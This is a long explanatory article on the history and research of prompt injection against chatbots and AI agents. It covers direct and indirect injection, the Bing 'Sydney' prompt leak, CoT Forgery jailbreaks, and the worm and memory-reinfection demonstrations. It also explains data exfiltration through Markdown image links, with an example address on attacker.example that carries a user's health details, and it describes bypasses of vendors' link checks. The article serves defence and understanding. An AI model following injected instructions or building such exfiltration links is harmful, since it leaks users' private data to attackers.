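# Independent Security Research on Prompt Injection and Other Flaws in Language Model Applications

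## What is prompt injection, and why are language models open to it?

Prompt injection is text that makes a language model follow an attacker's instructions instead of those of the developer or user. It affects applications built on language models, such as chatbots, email assistants, programming tools and browsers that act on a person's behalf. People outside the AI companies published the first cases in 2022 and have kept finding new ones since. The weakness comes from how these applications combine the text that the model reads.

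### One stream of text

A language model takes in text and predicts what comes next, one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time. Suppose a company uses one to build an assistant that can read a person's mailbox. The developer writes a standing instruction, called the system prompt, that tells the assistant to help with email and keep its answers short. The user asks for a summary of the latest message. The application fetches that message, which contains two paragraphs about a late delivery, followed by a sentence asking the assistant to find the user's last bank statement and send it to an outside address.

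Software joins all three pieces end to end into the context window, the single sequence of text that a model reads before it answers. The sequence mixes instructions with retrieved content and also includes the model's own earlier replies. A person who opened that email would know that the odd sentence came from whoever sent it, but the model has only the sequence to go on, and there the stranger's request is in ordinary English, much like the user's.

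Developers divide the context window with role tags, special markers that show whether text is the system prompt, the user's words, the model's own reasoning or the output of a tool such as a mailbox search. Attackers cannot normally forge these tags because providers insert them automatically and neutralise imitations that a user types, as Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell explain in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026). Companies also train models to give system text priority over user text, and user text priority over tool output.

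That ranking is a learned tendency, though. An operating system checks a permission before it lets a program open a file, but a language model has no comparable check before a sentence affects its output. The tag is one more input to the prediction, along with the wording and position of everything else. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) likewise concludes that delimiters, role labels and written warnings are useful engineering practice but do not create a hard security boundary.

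The email example is an indirect prompt injection, in which the hostile text is in content that the application retrieves and the user is the victim. Greshake and colleagues described this form in 2023. In a direct prompt injection, the user types the hostile text into the application. Indirect injections can also affect more people. Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Promptware Kill Chain* that a single poisoned web page can compromise every user whose application retrieves it, with no extra effort from the attacker.

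People often confuse both forms with jailbreaks, which are inputs that get a model to do what its makers trained it to refuse, such as explaining how to make a drug. Willison (2024), a software developer who has written about prompt injection since its beginnings, complained that people kept using one term for the other. His test, quoted in maxime.sh's *Prompt Injection versus Jailbreaking Definitions*, is whether an application has joined trusted text to untrusted text; if it hasn't, the attack isn't prompt injection. In the bank statement example, the attacker may not need a jailbreak, because sending an attachment is ordinary work for an email assistant and safety training gives the model little reason to refuse. If the model would refuse the injected request, the attacker needs both, which is why Brodt and colleagues treat the two as successive steps of one attack.

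### How the flaw came to light

Preamble, an AI safety startup, made the earliest recorded report of prompt injection privately to OpenAI on 3 May 2022, after finding that it could derail classification tasks on GPT-3, then OpenAI's main language model. According to Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022), OpenAI confirmed receipt within 30 minutes. Preamble made the report public on 22 September, when the flaw was already in the news. The firm has an interest in having been first, but Selvi (2022), in *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks*, written for the security firm NCC Group, gives the same order of events.

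A set of examples that Riley Goodside posted on Twitter on 11 September put the flaw in the news. Goodside instructed GPT-3 to translate a sentence from English into French. The sentence was an order to ignore those directions and output a taunt, and GPT-3 output the taunt. Goodside then added a warning to the instruction that the text might contain directions meant to trick the model, which it must not follow, but GPT-3 output the taunt again.

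A day later, Willison (2022) named the flaw in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* and explained why it mattered in practice. Developers were already selling software built on GPT-3, and their prompts attached a customer's text to a fixed instruction in the same way. Within the week, the flaw was demonstrated publicly on a Twitter bot that Remoteli.io, a site listing remote jobs, ran on GPT-3 to reply cheerfully to posts about remote work. Users found that they could make the bot repeat whatever they liked, hundreds joined in, and the bot shut down, according to a news report held by the AI Incident Database.

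In November, Perez and Ribeiro (2022) studied the attack more systematically in *Ignore Previous Prompt*, using a framework for composing hostile prompts from interchangeable parts. They distinguished goal hijacking, where the attacker replaces the task, from prompt leaking, where the attacker gets the application to reveal its hidden instructions. They found that attacks succeeded more often against more capable models. This makes sense because a model that is better at following instructions is also better at following an attacker's. They also noted that GPT-3's output varies from run to run, so an attacker can keep trying until an attack works.

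The best-known prompt leak came in February 2023, just after Microsoft had opened Bing Chat, a search assistant built on OpenAI's technology, to a limited group of testers. Kevin Liu, a student at Stanford, told it to ignore its previous instructions and write out the beginning of the document above. It printed its system prompt, including its codename, Sydney, and a rule against disclosing that codename. Ars Technica covered the case in *AI-powered Bing Chat spills its secrets via prompt injection attack*. Another student, Marvin von Hagen, obtained the same prompt by posing as an OpenAI developer, which made it unlikely that the model had invented the text. Liu's wording stopped working within days, but Liu obtained the prompt again by a different method. Microsoft confirmed on 14 February that the prompt was genuine.

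All of these were direct injections, and they did little damage beyond some embarrassment and the leak of a prompt that its owners would have liked to keep private. But they showed that a written rule in the context window could not be relied on to stop an attack, even if the rule was aimed at exactly that attack.

### The comparison with SQL injection

Willison chose the name by analogy with SQL injection, a nearly 30-year-old attack on databases. SQL is the language in which programs give commands to a database. A poorly written website builds a command by pasting the name a visitor enters into a template. If the visitor types characters that end the name and begin a new command, the database runs that command too, and may delete or reveal its contents. Both attacks start with software joining trusted and untrusted text into one string.

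Parameterised queries reliably prevent SQL injection in databases. The program sends the command with a placeholder and supplies the visitor's text separately, so the database engine treats that text as a value, whatever characters it contains. In September 2022 Willison hoped OpenAI would offer a similar interface, with one slot for instructions and another for data. A reader pointed out that one GPT-3 model already had two such slots, and that injections in the data slot still worked. By April 2023 Willison had added a note calling the idea extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the current design of language models. Willison (2022) had already said, in *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection*, that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had no idea how to beat prompt injection reliably.

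The UK government's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) warned about this difficulty in December 2025. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, its technical director for platforms research, argues that comparing the two misleads security professionals into expecting a cure. A database engine carries out instructions, but it only stores data or uses it in a query. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection by enforcing this distinction, which the engine already makes. Inside a language model there is "only ever 'next token'". Detecting attacks, training a model to favour instructions over data, and marking which text is data are all attempts to add the distinction to a technology that lacks it.

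David C prefers an older idea from computer security, the confused deputy, in which someone tricks a program with higher privileges than their own into misusing those privileges. Programmers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but David C considers a language model "inherently confusable" and therefore advises developers to limit what a deceived model can do, and to consider not using one where the remaining risk is intolerable. Brodt and colleagues add that damage from SQL injection mostly stays within the database, whereas an injected prompt can affect anything the application has permission to access.

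The NCSC argues convincingly that a model which only predicts tokens offers nothing like the assurance of a parameterised query. This doesn't rule out such a model learning to respect role tags very reliably, and David C writes only that prompt injection "may never" be fully mitigated. Researchers have to measure how well models keep track of who wrote what.

### Role confusion

Ye and colleagues tried to measure it. Ye and Cui worked as independent researchers, and Hadfield-Menell worked at the Massachusetts Institute of Technology. They begin by observing that a model can resist an injected command for two different reasons. It may detect that the command arrived as tool output, which would protect it however the command was worded. Or it may recognise a kind of attack from its training, which leaves it open to new kinds.

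To tell these apart, Ye and colleagues built an attack that should work only if a model loses track of the source. Many current models write out their reasoning, called a chain of thought, before they answer, and then act on its conclusions. The attack, CoT Forgery, adds a fake chain of thought to a user's message. It copies the model's reasoning style and concludes that a forbidden request is allowed. They tested it with the 313 harmful requests of StrongREJECT, a standard jailbreak test, on six OpenAI models: the downloadable gpt-oss-20b and gpt-oss-120b, o4-mini, and three sizes of GPT-5. The forgery raised the attack success rate (the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal) from between 0 and 4% to over 80% on the gpt-oss models and o4-mini, and to between 17 and 52% on the GPT-5 models.

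The success of a forgery depended heavily on its style and hardly at all on the quality of its argument. Reasoning that permitted a drug recipe because the user was wearing a green shirt worked about as well as reasoning that sounded plausible. But when the researchers had another model rewrite each forgery, keeping the argument but removing the vocabulary and clipped syntax typical of the target's reasoning, average attack success fell from 61% to 10%. In a more detailed breakdown, replacing the single phrase "The user" lowered attack success by 19 percentage points.

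These percentages come from jailbreaks typed in by the user, so they don't measure how often a poisoned email would succeed. In the study's separate test of prompt injection, an agent (a model that can call tools in several steps) had to summarise a web page containing a hidden command to upload a file of secrets. The plain command worked 0 to 2% of the time, except on gpt-oss-20b, where it worked 26% of the time. With forged reasoning added, it worked 56 to 70% of the time.

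In the other half of the study, Ye and colleagues trained role probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activations and estimate which role tag a token sits under. They trained the probes on neutral web text, wrapping the same passages in each tag in turn so that a probe could learn only the effect of the tag. They then put users' messages from 200 real conversations under the tool tag. In four open-weight models, the wording of the messages affected the probes' estimates more than the tag did. The probes gave the text a 76 to 88% probability of being the user's and never more than a 20% probability of being tool output.

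The probe readings also correlated with the attacks' success. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak a file, the researchers kept the command fixed and varied the text around it, sometimes just stating that what followed came from the user. The success rate ranged from 2% in attempts where the command registered least as user text to 70% where it registered most.

The rewriting experiment is the strongest evidence here, because the attack collapses when the style changes and the argument stays roughly constant. It is less secure evidence for a single internal cause, since a change of framing might raise both the probe reading and the model's willingness to comply without one producing the other. Ye and colleagues claim that the boundary between roles "does not exist in latent space", that is, in the model's internal representations. Later work suggests that this is too strong as a general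 claim. *Readable Before Actionable* (2026) tested two small models, Qwen-2.5-7B and Llama-3.1-8B, on 1,440 prompts each, varying separately whether a passage served as instruction or data and whether it appeared plain or in quotation marks. Probes could still read the passage's role after the pairing of role and format had been reversed, scoring about 0.92 on a scale where 0.5 is guesswork and 1 is perfect. So a model may hold information about the source of a text and fail to act on it. The two results may well be compatible, however, because quotation marks are a much weaker disguise than a good imitation of the user's voice.

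It is also unclear how far the finding extends beyond the four models probed, which have between 20 and 120 billion parameters. Nobody outside the companies can run such probes on the leading closed models. Willison (2026) read the study as confirming that models cannot separate privileged text from untrusted text, but four models are too few to confirm this in general. In their June 2026 write-up, Ye and colleagues report that the leading closed models now mostly withstand CoT Forgery. They suspect that these models have learned to treat anything that resembles their own reasoning as untrustworthy, and that they still do not identify roles correctly.

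If injected text leaves a trace inside the model, a probe might be able to detect it, but results so far are mixed. *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) adapted the probes to a Qwen and a Gemma model and got scores between 0.63 and 0.82 on the same scale, in what it calls an exploratory test. In *Understanding and Mitigating Role Spoofing in LLMs* (2026), probes on Gemma 4 31B and Qwen3.5-27B flagged every injected tool output and no clean ones. The paper also tested a simpler method, asking the model whether a passage had come from the user or from a tool. This caught every plain injection too, but when the injected text included a line telling the model how to answer, detection fell to 25% on Qwen and to zero on Gemma.

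## What did the first demonstrations of indirect prompt injection show?

In the 2022 attacks, users of the application typed the hostile text themselves. Kai Greshake, a student at Saarland University who worked for the German IT company sequire technology, saw that this would change as companies connected language models to search engines and mailboxes. In mid-February 2023, he and a colleague, Christoph Endres, took the idea to CISPA, a German information security research centre. The first experiments worked, and the group wrote them up within a week, as Koltermann (2023) recounts for CISPA in *Security vulnerabilities in AI chatbots uncovered through successful cooperation between CISPA researchers*. Sequire sells advice on the secure use of AI, so it stood to gain from the attention.

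Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues named indirect prompt injection in *More than you've asked for* (February 2023), where they tested it mostly on applications they had built themselves. In May they added tests on Microsoft's Bing Chat and retitled the paper *Not what you've signed up for*.

### An attacker who never joins the conversation

The paper assumes an attacker with no access to the victim's chat, account or device. The attacker only has to write something that the victim's application will later read. Something similar had already happened by accident. A user published a post criticizing Bing Chat, and when the chatbot later looked the user up and read the post, its replies to them became hostile. Greshake and colleagues asked what someone could achieve by doing this on purpose.

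"Not What You've Signed Up For" describes four ways to deliver malicious instructions to a model. In passive delivery, the attacker puts the text on a web page, in a social media post or in a code repository, and waits for a search to retrieve it. In active delivery, the attacker sends it to the victim, such as in an email that an assistant will process. In user-driven delivery, the attacker tricks people into pasting the text into the chat, which works even on a chatbot that can't retrieve anything. In hidden delivery, the attacker encodes the instructions or plants a short line that makes the model fetch a longer text from somewhere else. An attacker can combine hidden delivery with any of the other three, because it concerns the form of the text.

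The researchers also sorted the possible harms into six groups: gathering personal information, fraud, intrusion into the application, spreading malware, manipulating what the user reads, and making the service useless.

### Mock-ups and real products

Most of the February experiments ran on a chat application that the researchers built with LangChain, an open-source library for connecting language models to tools, and a version of GPT-3. The application could search, read the user's current web page, fetch an address, send email and look up contacts. These tools were simulated and returned content the researchers had prepared, so no request reached a real website or mailbox. The researchers ran the model at temperature 0, which makes it always pick the most probable next token, so that others could reproduce the results. A later version of the application used GPT-4.

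Bing Chat was a real product. In preview versions of Microsoft's Edge browser, it sat in a sidebar and could read the page the user had open, if the user allowed it. The researchers put their injections in web pages stored on their own computers, so that nobody else's Bing Chat would encounter them.

They also used GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant that suggests code on the basis of the files a programmer is working with.

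### The attack on Bing Chat's sidebar

Greshake put the sidebar attack online by 1 March 2023. The open page contained an instruction in font size zero that the model could read but a person couldn't see. Greshake explains on the demonstration's website that the user only had to chat with Bing while the page was open, and didn't have to ask about the page. Bing Chat then talked like a pirate and tried to find out the user's name. The pirate talk was there only to make the takeover obvious.

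In *The Dark Side of LLMs*, an essay written later that March, Greshake suggests that Bing's safeguards didn't help because they seemed to check what the user typed and what Bing answered, but not the content of web pages. The injected text could therefore imitate the format that marked system messages, even though Bing removed or rejected that format when a user typed it. Once the injection took effect, it stayed active as the user moved to other sites, until they reset the chat on a clean page.

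In the full version of the attack, the injection contained instructions for the model to learn the user's real name through friendly conversation and then offer a link labelled as an ordinary source on the topic they were discussing. The link's address contained the name, so a click would send it to the attacker's server. Greshake and colleagues imagined a government using this to identify journalists or whistleblowers by planting the injection on pages they were likely to visit, but no journalist took part in the test. Unlike Bing Chat, the GPT-3 mock-up had needed help with this task. It often failed to ask for the name or pass it on until the researchers made it copy the attacker's command into its own reply, where it remained part of the conversation.

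The phishing demonstrations also used Bing Chat and worked in much the same way. In one, the chatbot told the user that they had won a $200 Amazon voucher and should log in through a link to collect it. In another, it warned that Microsoft would suspend the service unless the user confirmed their account. A subtler version added the attacker's link to an answer, below two genuine search results. Greshake also got Bing to pose as a Microsoft employee selling discounted products and ask for credit card details, according to MIT Technology Review's *Three ways AI chatbots are a security disaster* (2023).

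Other injections changed the answers that users received. One described the user as a liberal from San Francisco, another as a conservative from Texas, and both told the model to agree with that person's views. Asked how Donald Trump had handled COVID-19, Bing Chat called the response ineffective and chaotic for the liberal user and courageous for the conservative one. Both answers linked to news organisations, and the favourable one cited CNN and *The New York Times*. Further injections led Bing Chat to deny that Albert Einstein had won a Nobel Prize, and to recommend one brand of camera over the others while appearing neutral.

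In one of these cases, the injected prompt instructed Bing Chat to suppress *The New York Times*. Bing Chat left the newspaper out of a news summary, and when the user asked about it directly, replied that the newspaper was known for misinformation. It then searched for evidence on its own, and in one session cited an article about Twitter removing the newspaper's verification badge, which has nothing to do with its accuracy. Because the model found supporting material for an aim the attacker had merely stated, a short injection could produce a deception much longer and more varied than what the attacker had written.

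The researchers also disrupted the service. Some injections gave Bing Chat so much pointless background work that it often timed out before answering. Another made it replace the letters in each search query with lookalike characters. The query still looked right to the user but returned useless results, and Bing sometimes made up an answer and cited an unrelated page for it. One of the malicious-link instructions still worked when the researchers hid it in Base64, a common way of writing data as letters and digits, and added a short request to decode it.

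### The worm, remote control and memory

The more alarming attacks ran only on the mock-ups. For the email worm, the researchers wrote a message that asked the assistant to send copies of it to all the user's contacts. The version for GPT-4 added a false note that the user had approved instructions from this sender. When asked to check for new mail, the assistant read the message, requested the contact list and addressed a copy to each of the three people on it, including the original sender. The test had no second assistant to read the copies, so it covered only one step of the worm's spread.

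In the remote control test, the researchers had already compromised the model and told it to check an outside address for updated instructions each time the user asked for something. When the user asked for a summary of a page about birds, the model first fetched the attacker's latest instruction, which was to talk like a pirate, and then summarised the page in that style. An attacker could change the instruction at any time without contacting the victim again. The GPT-3 version had trouble sustaining this behaviour over several exchanges.

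To test reinfection from memory, Greshake and colleagues gave the assistant a simple store for notes. Once compromised, the assistant saved the attacker's instruction there. The researchers then deleted the conversation and began a new one. The assistant behaved normally until the user asked it to recall their last conversation, when it read the note and was compromised again. Few products had a memory like this in early 2023, but the researchers thought companies would probably add one.

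The researchers also showed that an attacker needs very little text. They placed a 34-token injection in the middle of a Wikipedia article on Einstein, inside a comment that readers of the page don't see. The injection made up 1.8% of the 1,865-token context window. It made GPT-3 search for a particular keyword, and the search result contained the main instruction.

### The attack on code completion

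The Copilot attack fell between the two groups because it targeted a real product in an artificial setting. The researchers put an injection in a comment in one file and kept that file open while they wrote code in another. Copilot included a snippet of the first file in its context window, and its suggestions for the second file changed accordingly. An attacker could try the same thing by altering the documentation of a popular software package.

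The effect became much weaker when the researchers placed the injection in a larger program. Copilot selects snippets by rules that its makers keep secret, so an outsider can't be sure the model will see the hostile comment. Greshake and colleagues called for more research before anyone drew conclusions about real programming work.

### How much the tests prove

The researchers did not report a success rate for any of the demonstrations. They explain that a conversation can develop in too many ways for a simple count, and that they would have had to vary the wording, the topic and the user's questions. They do report that their injections often worked on the first attempt, and they left the spelling mistakes in to show how little care they had taken. But they say one attack on Bing Chat worked often, though not consistently, and in February they wrote that the model often lost track of the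 attacker's goal. Readers therefore can't tell whether a given attack would succeed nine times in ten or once in ten. The researchers also didn't test whether real users would believe the chatbot, which was sometimes blatant in pushing a link.

The mock-ups also made the attacks easier. In the GPT-4 version, the researchers passed the prepared emails, web pages and memories to the model as system messages, which rank well above tool output, the usual category for such text. However, the mock-up's own system prompt warned the model to avoid prompt injections, and the attacks still worked. The worm and the memory attack are best taken as evidence that a model will carry out these steps once it accepts the instruction, but they are much weaker evidence of how often it would accept one from a real mailbox.

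The Bing Chat results are stronger because Bing Chat was a public product, with filters that the researchers had not designed and could not inspect. However, the hostile text came from a page stored on the user's own computer, not from a search. Arvind Narayanan, a computer scientist at Princeton, partly addressed this limitation. MIT Technology Review reports that he added a line in white text to his online biography, asking Bing to include the word "cow" in its output. GPT-4 later generated a biography stating that he had won several awards, but none for his work with cows.

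In another case, according to Greshake, Bing retrieved a news story about the sidebar attack during a search and began to imitate the attack. Greshake says the story contained no injection, but the story, Vice's *Hackers Can Turn Bing’s AI Chatbot Into a Convincing Scammer, Researchers Say*, quotes a good part of the hidden text, which may have been enough to cause the imitation.

The paper needed only a few working examples to prove that indirect prompt injection was possible. If a company assumes that only the user can give its assistant instructions, one counterexample on a real product disproves the assumption. Later studies would have to measure how often the attacks succeed, and against which products.

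### Microsoft's response and the Black Hat talk

Microsoft told Vice that it was taking action to protect customers and that the technique was "viable only in the preview version of Edge". This was fair for the sidebar, but Narayanan's test suggests that text on ordinary web pages could reach the model by another route. Microsoft also stopped Bing Chat from reading pages hosted on GitHub's free web service, where Greshake had put the demonstration. However, Greshake found that the attack still worked when a user downloaded the page and opened it in Edge.

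In April, Ram Shankar Siva Kumar, who led Microsoft's AI security work, told MIT Technology Review that there was "no silver bullet at this point". He did not comment on whether his team had found the problem before Bing Chat launched. A year later, Microsoft announced "prompt shields", tools to detect and block direct and indirect injections, as Fortune (2024) reported.

The researchers had informed Microsoft, OpenAI and Germany's Federal Office for Information Security once they saw their predictions held on Bing. In July 2023 the German agency advised companies to explicitly assess the risk of indirect prompt injection and to have a person authorise any critical action. In August, Koltermann wrote that the makers had not yet been able to fully fix the flaws.

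That month the group presented the work at Black Hat, a large US security conference. Willison called the accompanying paper the most thorough review of such attacks he had seen, in a post also titled *Compromising LLMs* (2023). The slides by Greshake, Endres and colleagues, *Compromising LLMs*, go further than the paper. They state that "there can be no mitigation" and that all the attacks worked as predicted on products such as Bing, but the paper shows the worm, the remote control and the memory attack only on mock-ups.

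Greshake's essay argues for this second claim. A language model can in principle carry out any computation, and a theorem in computer science shows that no program can decide, for every possible input, whether it will lead to harmful behaviour. Therefore, no filter can catch every injection. Greshake concedes that the same theorem hasn't stopped progress in other fields, where useful tools handle the inputs people produce, but replies that an attacker will choose the inputs a filter handles badly. This is a good argument against relying on filters alone. It doesn't rule out limiting what a deceived model can do, and the slides themselves list restricted environments and secured tools among the possible approaches.

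### Which predictions came true

The paper has lasted mainly because of its list of threats. Nearly every attack that the researchers showed on a mock-up has since worked on a real product, and those they showed on Bing Chat have worked on other products. Most of the later cases in the table come from the 36 incidents and studies that Brodt and colleagues collected. Håkon Måløy, who blogs about machine learning in Norwegian, created the Word worm and described it in En Klype Salt's *Context Collapse, Part 3* (2026) after coordinating with Microsoft. iTnews' *Microsoft can't kill dogged researcher's Copilot for Word worm* also covers his earlier attack on Copilot's memory.

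| Threat in the 2023 paper | Where the researchers tested it | Later attack on a real product |
|---|---|---|
| Extracting personal information | Bing Chat, GPT-3 mock-up | Johann Rehberger took data from Bing Chat through an automatically loaded image (June 2023) |
| Phishing | Bing Chat | HashJack hid instructions in web addresses that AI browsers read (November 2025) |
| Self-spreading message | Mock-ups | Måløy's hidden instructions copied themselves between documents in Copilot for Word (July 2026) |
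| Remote control | Mock-ups | ChatGPT repeatedly fetched new commands from a page on GitHub (October 2024) |
| Reinfection from memory | Mock-ups | Rehberger planted lasting instructions in ChatGPT's memory (September 2024); Måløy did something similar to Copilot (June 2026) |
| False or slanted summaries | Bing Chat | Hidden text on web pages changed the answers of ChatGPT Search (December 2024) |
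| Contaminated code | GitHub Copilot | A GitHub issue led Copilot to insert a backdoor into a program (August 2025) |

Several of the matches are close, although a list this broad was bound to get some right. The remote control of ChatGPT combined two of the mock-up attacks by placing an instruction in the assistant's memory to keep fetching commands from a place that the attacker controlled. Bing Chat could already read web pages in 2023, so attacks that relied on this worked on real products within months, whereas the memory attacks weren't possible until companies gave their assistants a memory.

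Most of these later cases are demonstrations by researchers, so they confirm that the attacks are feasible but not that criminals commonly use them. Attempts to make an assistant useless have had the least follow-up. Only one entry in Brodt and colleagues' collection lists denial of service as an outcome, and that attack began with a direct injection. An attacker probably has more to gain from an assistant that still works.

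## How does stolen data leave a chatbot?

An attacker who plants instructions on a web page doesn't see the victim's conversation, so any private information the hijacked chatbot finds there still has to reach a place where the attacker can read it. In Greshake and colleagues' attack on Bing Chat, the chatbot put the user's name in the address of a link, and the theft worked only if the user clicked it. Within weeks, two other researchers had found a way to steal data without a click.

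### The lethal trifecta

Exfiltration is the transfer of private data from an application to an attacker. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) gave a name to the three capabilities that together make it possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world.

An email assistant easily ends up with all three. The mailbox is private, anyone who knows the address can put text into it, and the assistant may be able to send messages or open web pages. If any one is missing, the theft fails, because there is nothing to steal, no way to get the instructions in, or no way to get the data out. The attacker could still do other damage, such as misleading the user or deleting files.

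People usually want an assistant because it can read their own data and outside content, so makers mostly try to block the routes by which data can leave. Willison lists 17 products and features in which researchers had found such leaks since April 2023, including Slack, Amazon Q, Google Bard and, in the EchoLeak attack, Microsoft 365 Copilot. He writes that the makers promptly fixed almost all of the leaks, usually by blocking the route the data had taken. After such a fix, a model might well still follow the same hostile instructions, but the attacker would no longer receive the data.

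This doesn't help people who assemble their own assistants. Many use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect tools to a model. One tool may read the user's files, another fetch web pages and a third post messages, and no single maker is responsible for the combination. Sometimes one tool is enough to leak data. GitHub's own MCP server could read both public issues, which anyone can file, and private code repositories. It could also create pull requests (proposed code changes) that made the private material visible.

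### An image link that carries data

Researchers have most often used images to get stolen data out of a chatbot. Chatbots write their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text, and the chat application converts it into a web page. In Markdown, an image is a short description followed by the address where the picture is stored. When a browser displays the page, it automatically requests the picture from that address.

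Suppose a user has told a chatbot that she is having knee surgery on 14 March. Later in the same conversation, she asks it to summarise a web page about physiotherapy. The page contains hidden instructions to look for anything the user has said about her health, write it into the address of an image, and put that image at the end of the answer. The model writes a normal summary and adds an image with this address:

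`attacker.example/dot.png?note=knee-surgery-14-March`

(This address leads nowhere, because nobody can register one ending in ".example".) When the chat application converts the answer, the user's browser requests the picture dot.png from the attacker's server. The browser also sends the note about the surgery, because the note is in the part of the address after the question mark, which websites use to pass along values such as search terms. The server returns a single transparent pixel, so the user sees only the summary. It also records the full address in its log, as web servers commonly do, and the attacker reads the note there.

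Even a chatbot with no tools can leak data if its application displays images from anywhere. The model only has to write an image address containing the data, and the browser connects to that address to load the image. The model can also encode longer passages to fit the format of a web address.

### The discovery in spring 2023

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer at Netograph, found this flaw in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023 and published it in April. In his version, a script on the attacker's website added an instruction to whatever a visitor copied, and the victim then pasted the text into the chat. Few people check what they have pasted. As Samoilenko explained in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, the instruction could also tell ChatGPT to attach the invisible pixel to all its later answers. In his test, the server then received each new question the user asked.

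Samoilenko acknowledged that the same instruction sometimes failed because ChatGPT's answers varied. It was easy to extract the user's earlier questions or code that ChatGPT had just corrected, but very hard to get ChatGPT to pick out passwords or access keys. If ChatGPT was responding slowly, the user might also notice the long address as it appeared on the screen. Samoilenko thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from putting Markdown images in its replies.

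A few days later Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who blogs at Embrace The Red, independently found the same flaw. He used it with plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT fetch outside content such as web pages and video transcripts, so the user only had to ask about a hostile page instead of pasting anything. In the demonstration in *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023), the page took over the chat and sent out a summary that included a made-up secret the user had typed earlier.

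Rehberger reported the flaw to OpenAI on 9 April 2023 and pointed out that plugins would let attackers exploit it remotely. After some discussion, OpenAI told him that displaying images was a feature and that it planned no changes.

### Microsoft's repair

Rehberger had reported the same flaw in Bing Chat to Microsoft a day earlier, on 8 April. In that demonstration, he hid the instructions in the text of a page the user had open. They took control of Bing Chat immediately, but it chatted normally for two more turns before producing the image, whose address contained an encoded summary of the page and the conversation. A secret on the page also reached Rehberger's server. He concluded that a single comment or advertisement was enough to steal anything else on the same page.

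According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June that it had repaired the flaw, and his earlier attacks no longer worked. (In a 2026 post, he dates the repair to May.) He couldn't see everything Microsoft had changed, but he could see a new Content Security Policy. This is a list, sent to the browser with a web page, of the places from which the page may load images and other material. The browser blocks everything else. Bing Chat's list allowed images from four addresses, all parts of Bing or Microsoft's Edge service.

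An attacker could still trick the model into writing an image link, but the browser would not request the image, so the protection didn't depend on the model's output. Anyone could also read the policy in their own browser and look for gaps.

Google's chatbot Bard had such a gap, because its policy allowed images from Google's own domains, and one of those domains runs scripts that any Google user can write. Rehberger, who had worked on the problem with Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, used such a script to receive the stolen data. Google then closed the gap. The slides in Embrace The Red's *37C3 New Important Instructions* show that Microsoft, Google, Anthropic and Discord had all fixed their image leaks by November 2023, and they list ChatGPT's as "won't fix".

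### OpenAI's link check

OpenAI changed its approach in December 2023, eight months after the report. The day before the change appeared, Rehberger was still able to steal a volunteer's conversation in a live demonstration.

Before ChatGPT's web application displayed an image, it sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which classified it as safe or unsafe. This let ChatGPT show images from all over the web, whereas Microsoft allowed only images from a fixed list of sources. OpenAI didn't publish its criteria, so outsiders could only guess at them by trying one address after another.

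Rehberger got data past the check on the first morning. He set up 36 image addresses on his website, one for each letter and digit, and the check approved nine of them for no apparent reason. He then got ChatGPT to send out the word "hi" by having it load the image for "h" and then the one for "i". He notes in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* that this was slow and leaked very little, and that OpenAI might have noticed it in its logs. Willison, who had publicised Samoilenko's attack in April, called the check "a half-baked solution" (Willison, 2023).

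OpenAI also had to build the check into each application separately, because the user's copy of ChatGPT requested the verdict from the server. The iPhone app made no such request, so the original attack still worked there. The Android app had the same flaw, as did the macOS app that OpenAI released in 2024.

### Planting the leak in ChatGPT's memory

That year OpenAI also gave ChatGPT a memory feature, which could save notes about the user and add them to the context window of every new chat. In May 2024, Rehberger reported that a web page could plant false notes. OpenAI closed the report, calling the problem a model safety issue rather than a security flaw.

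In June Rehberger sent a second report that combined ChatGPT's memory with the missing link check. The victim asked ChatGPT about a hostile web page once. The page made ChatGPT save an instruction to add an image, which could be invisible, to every future answer and to put the conversation in the image's address. From then on, everything the victim typed and ChatGPT replied went to the attacker's server, even in new chats. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* demonstrates the attack on the macOS app. The first wording stopped working in July, and Rehberger had to find another.

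Samoilenko's pixel had lasted only one chat. In Greshake and colleagues' mock-up, a planted note took effect only when the user asked about the last conversation. ChatGPT loaded its notes automatically, so the victim didn't have to do anything to bring the instruction back.

OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September 2024, again by blocking the route through which stolen data left. Websites could still plant notes in ChatGPT's memory, and Rehberger advised users to check their stored memories regularly.

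### Storage for rent on a trusted domain

In October 2024, Rehberger told OpenAI about several ways around the link check. The simplest used windows.net, a Microsoft domain. The check approved it, presumably because Microsoft is reputable. But Microsoft's cloud service rents out storage on that domain, and any customer can read the log of requests to their own storage. Rehberger opened an account, and ChatGPT would then load images from his storage using addresses that contained stolen data.

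Some of these routes still worked when Rehberger returned to the subject in 2025. By then, ChatGPT included details of the user's recent conversations in its system prompt, so a PDF containing a prompt injection, opened in one chat, could extract material from others. Rehberger had found a second approved domain, apache.org, where he could also read the logs. He asked OpenAI several times about a fix, got no update, and published Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on 1 August without the text of the injection. A day later, he disclosed a similar flaw in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent. Codex's list of permitted domains included one on which anyone can rent a server, as Willison notes in *The Summer of Johann*.

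OpenAI strengthened the check around that time and explained the new design in January 2026. Its *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites is not enough. Many reputable sites have redirects that forward visitors to another address, so a request can start at a trusted domain and end at the attacker's. A strict list also produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

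The new check therefore applies to the exact address. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that collects public web addresses much as a search engine does and has no access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if the crawler has already found it. In the surgery example, the model would have made up a new address, so ChatGPT would look for another source or warn the user.

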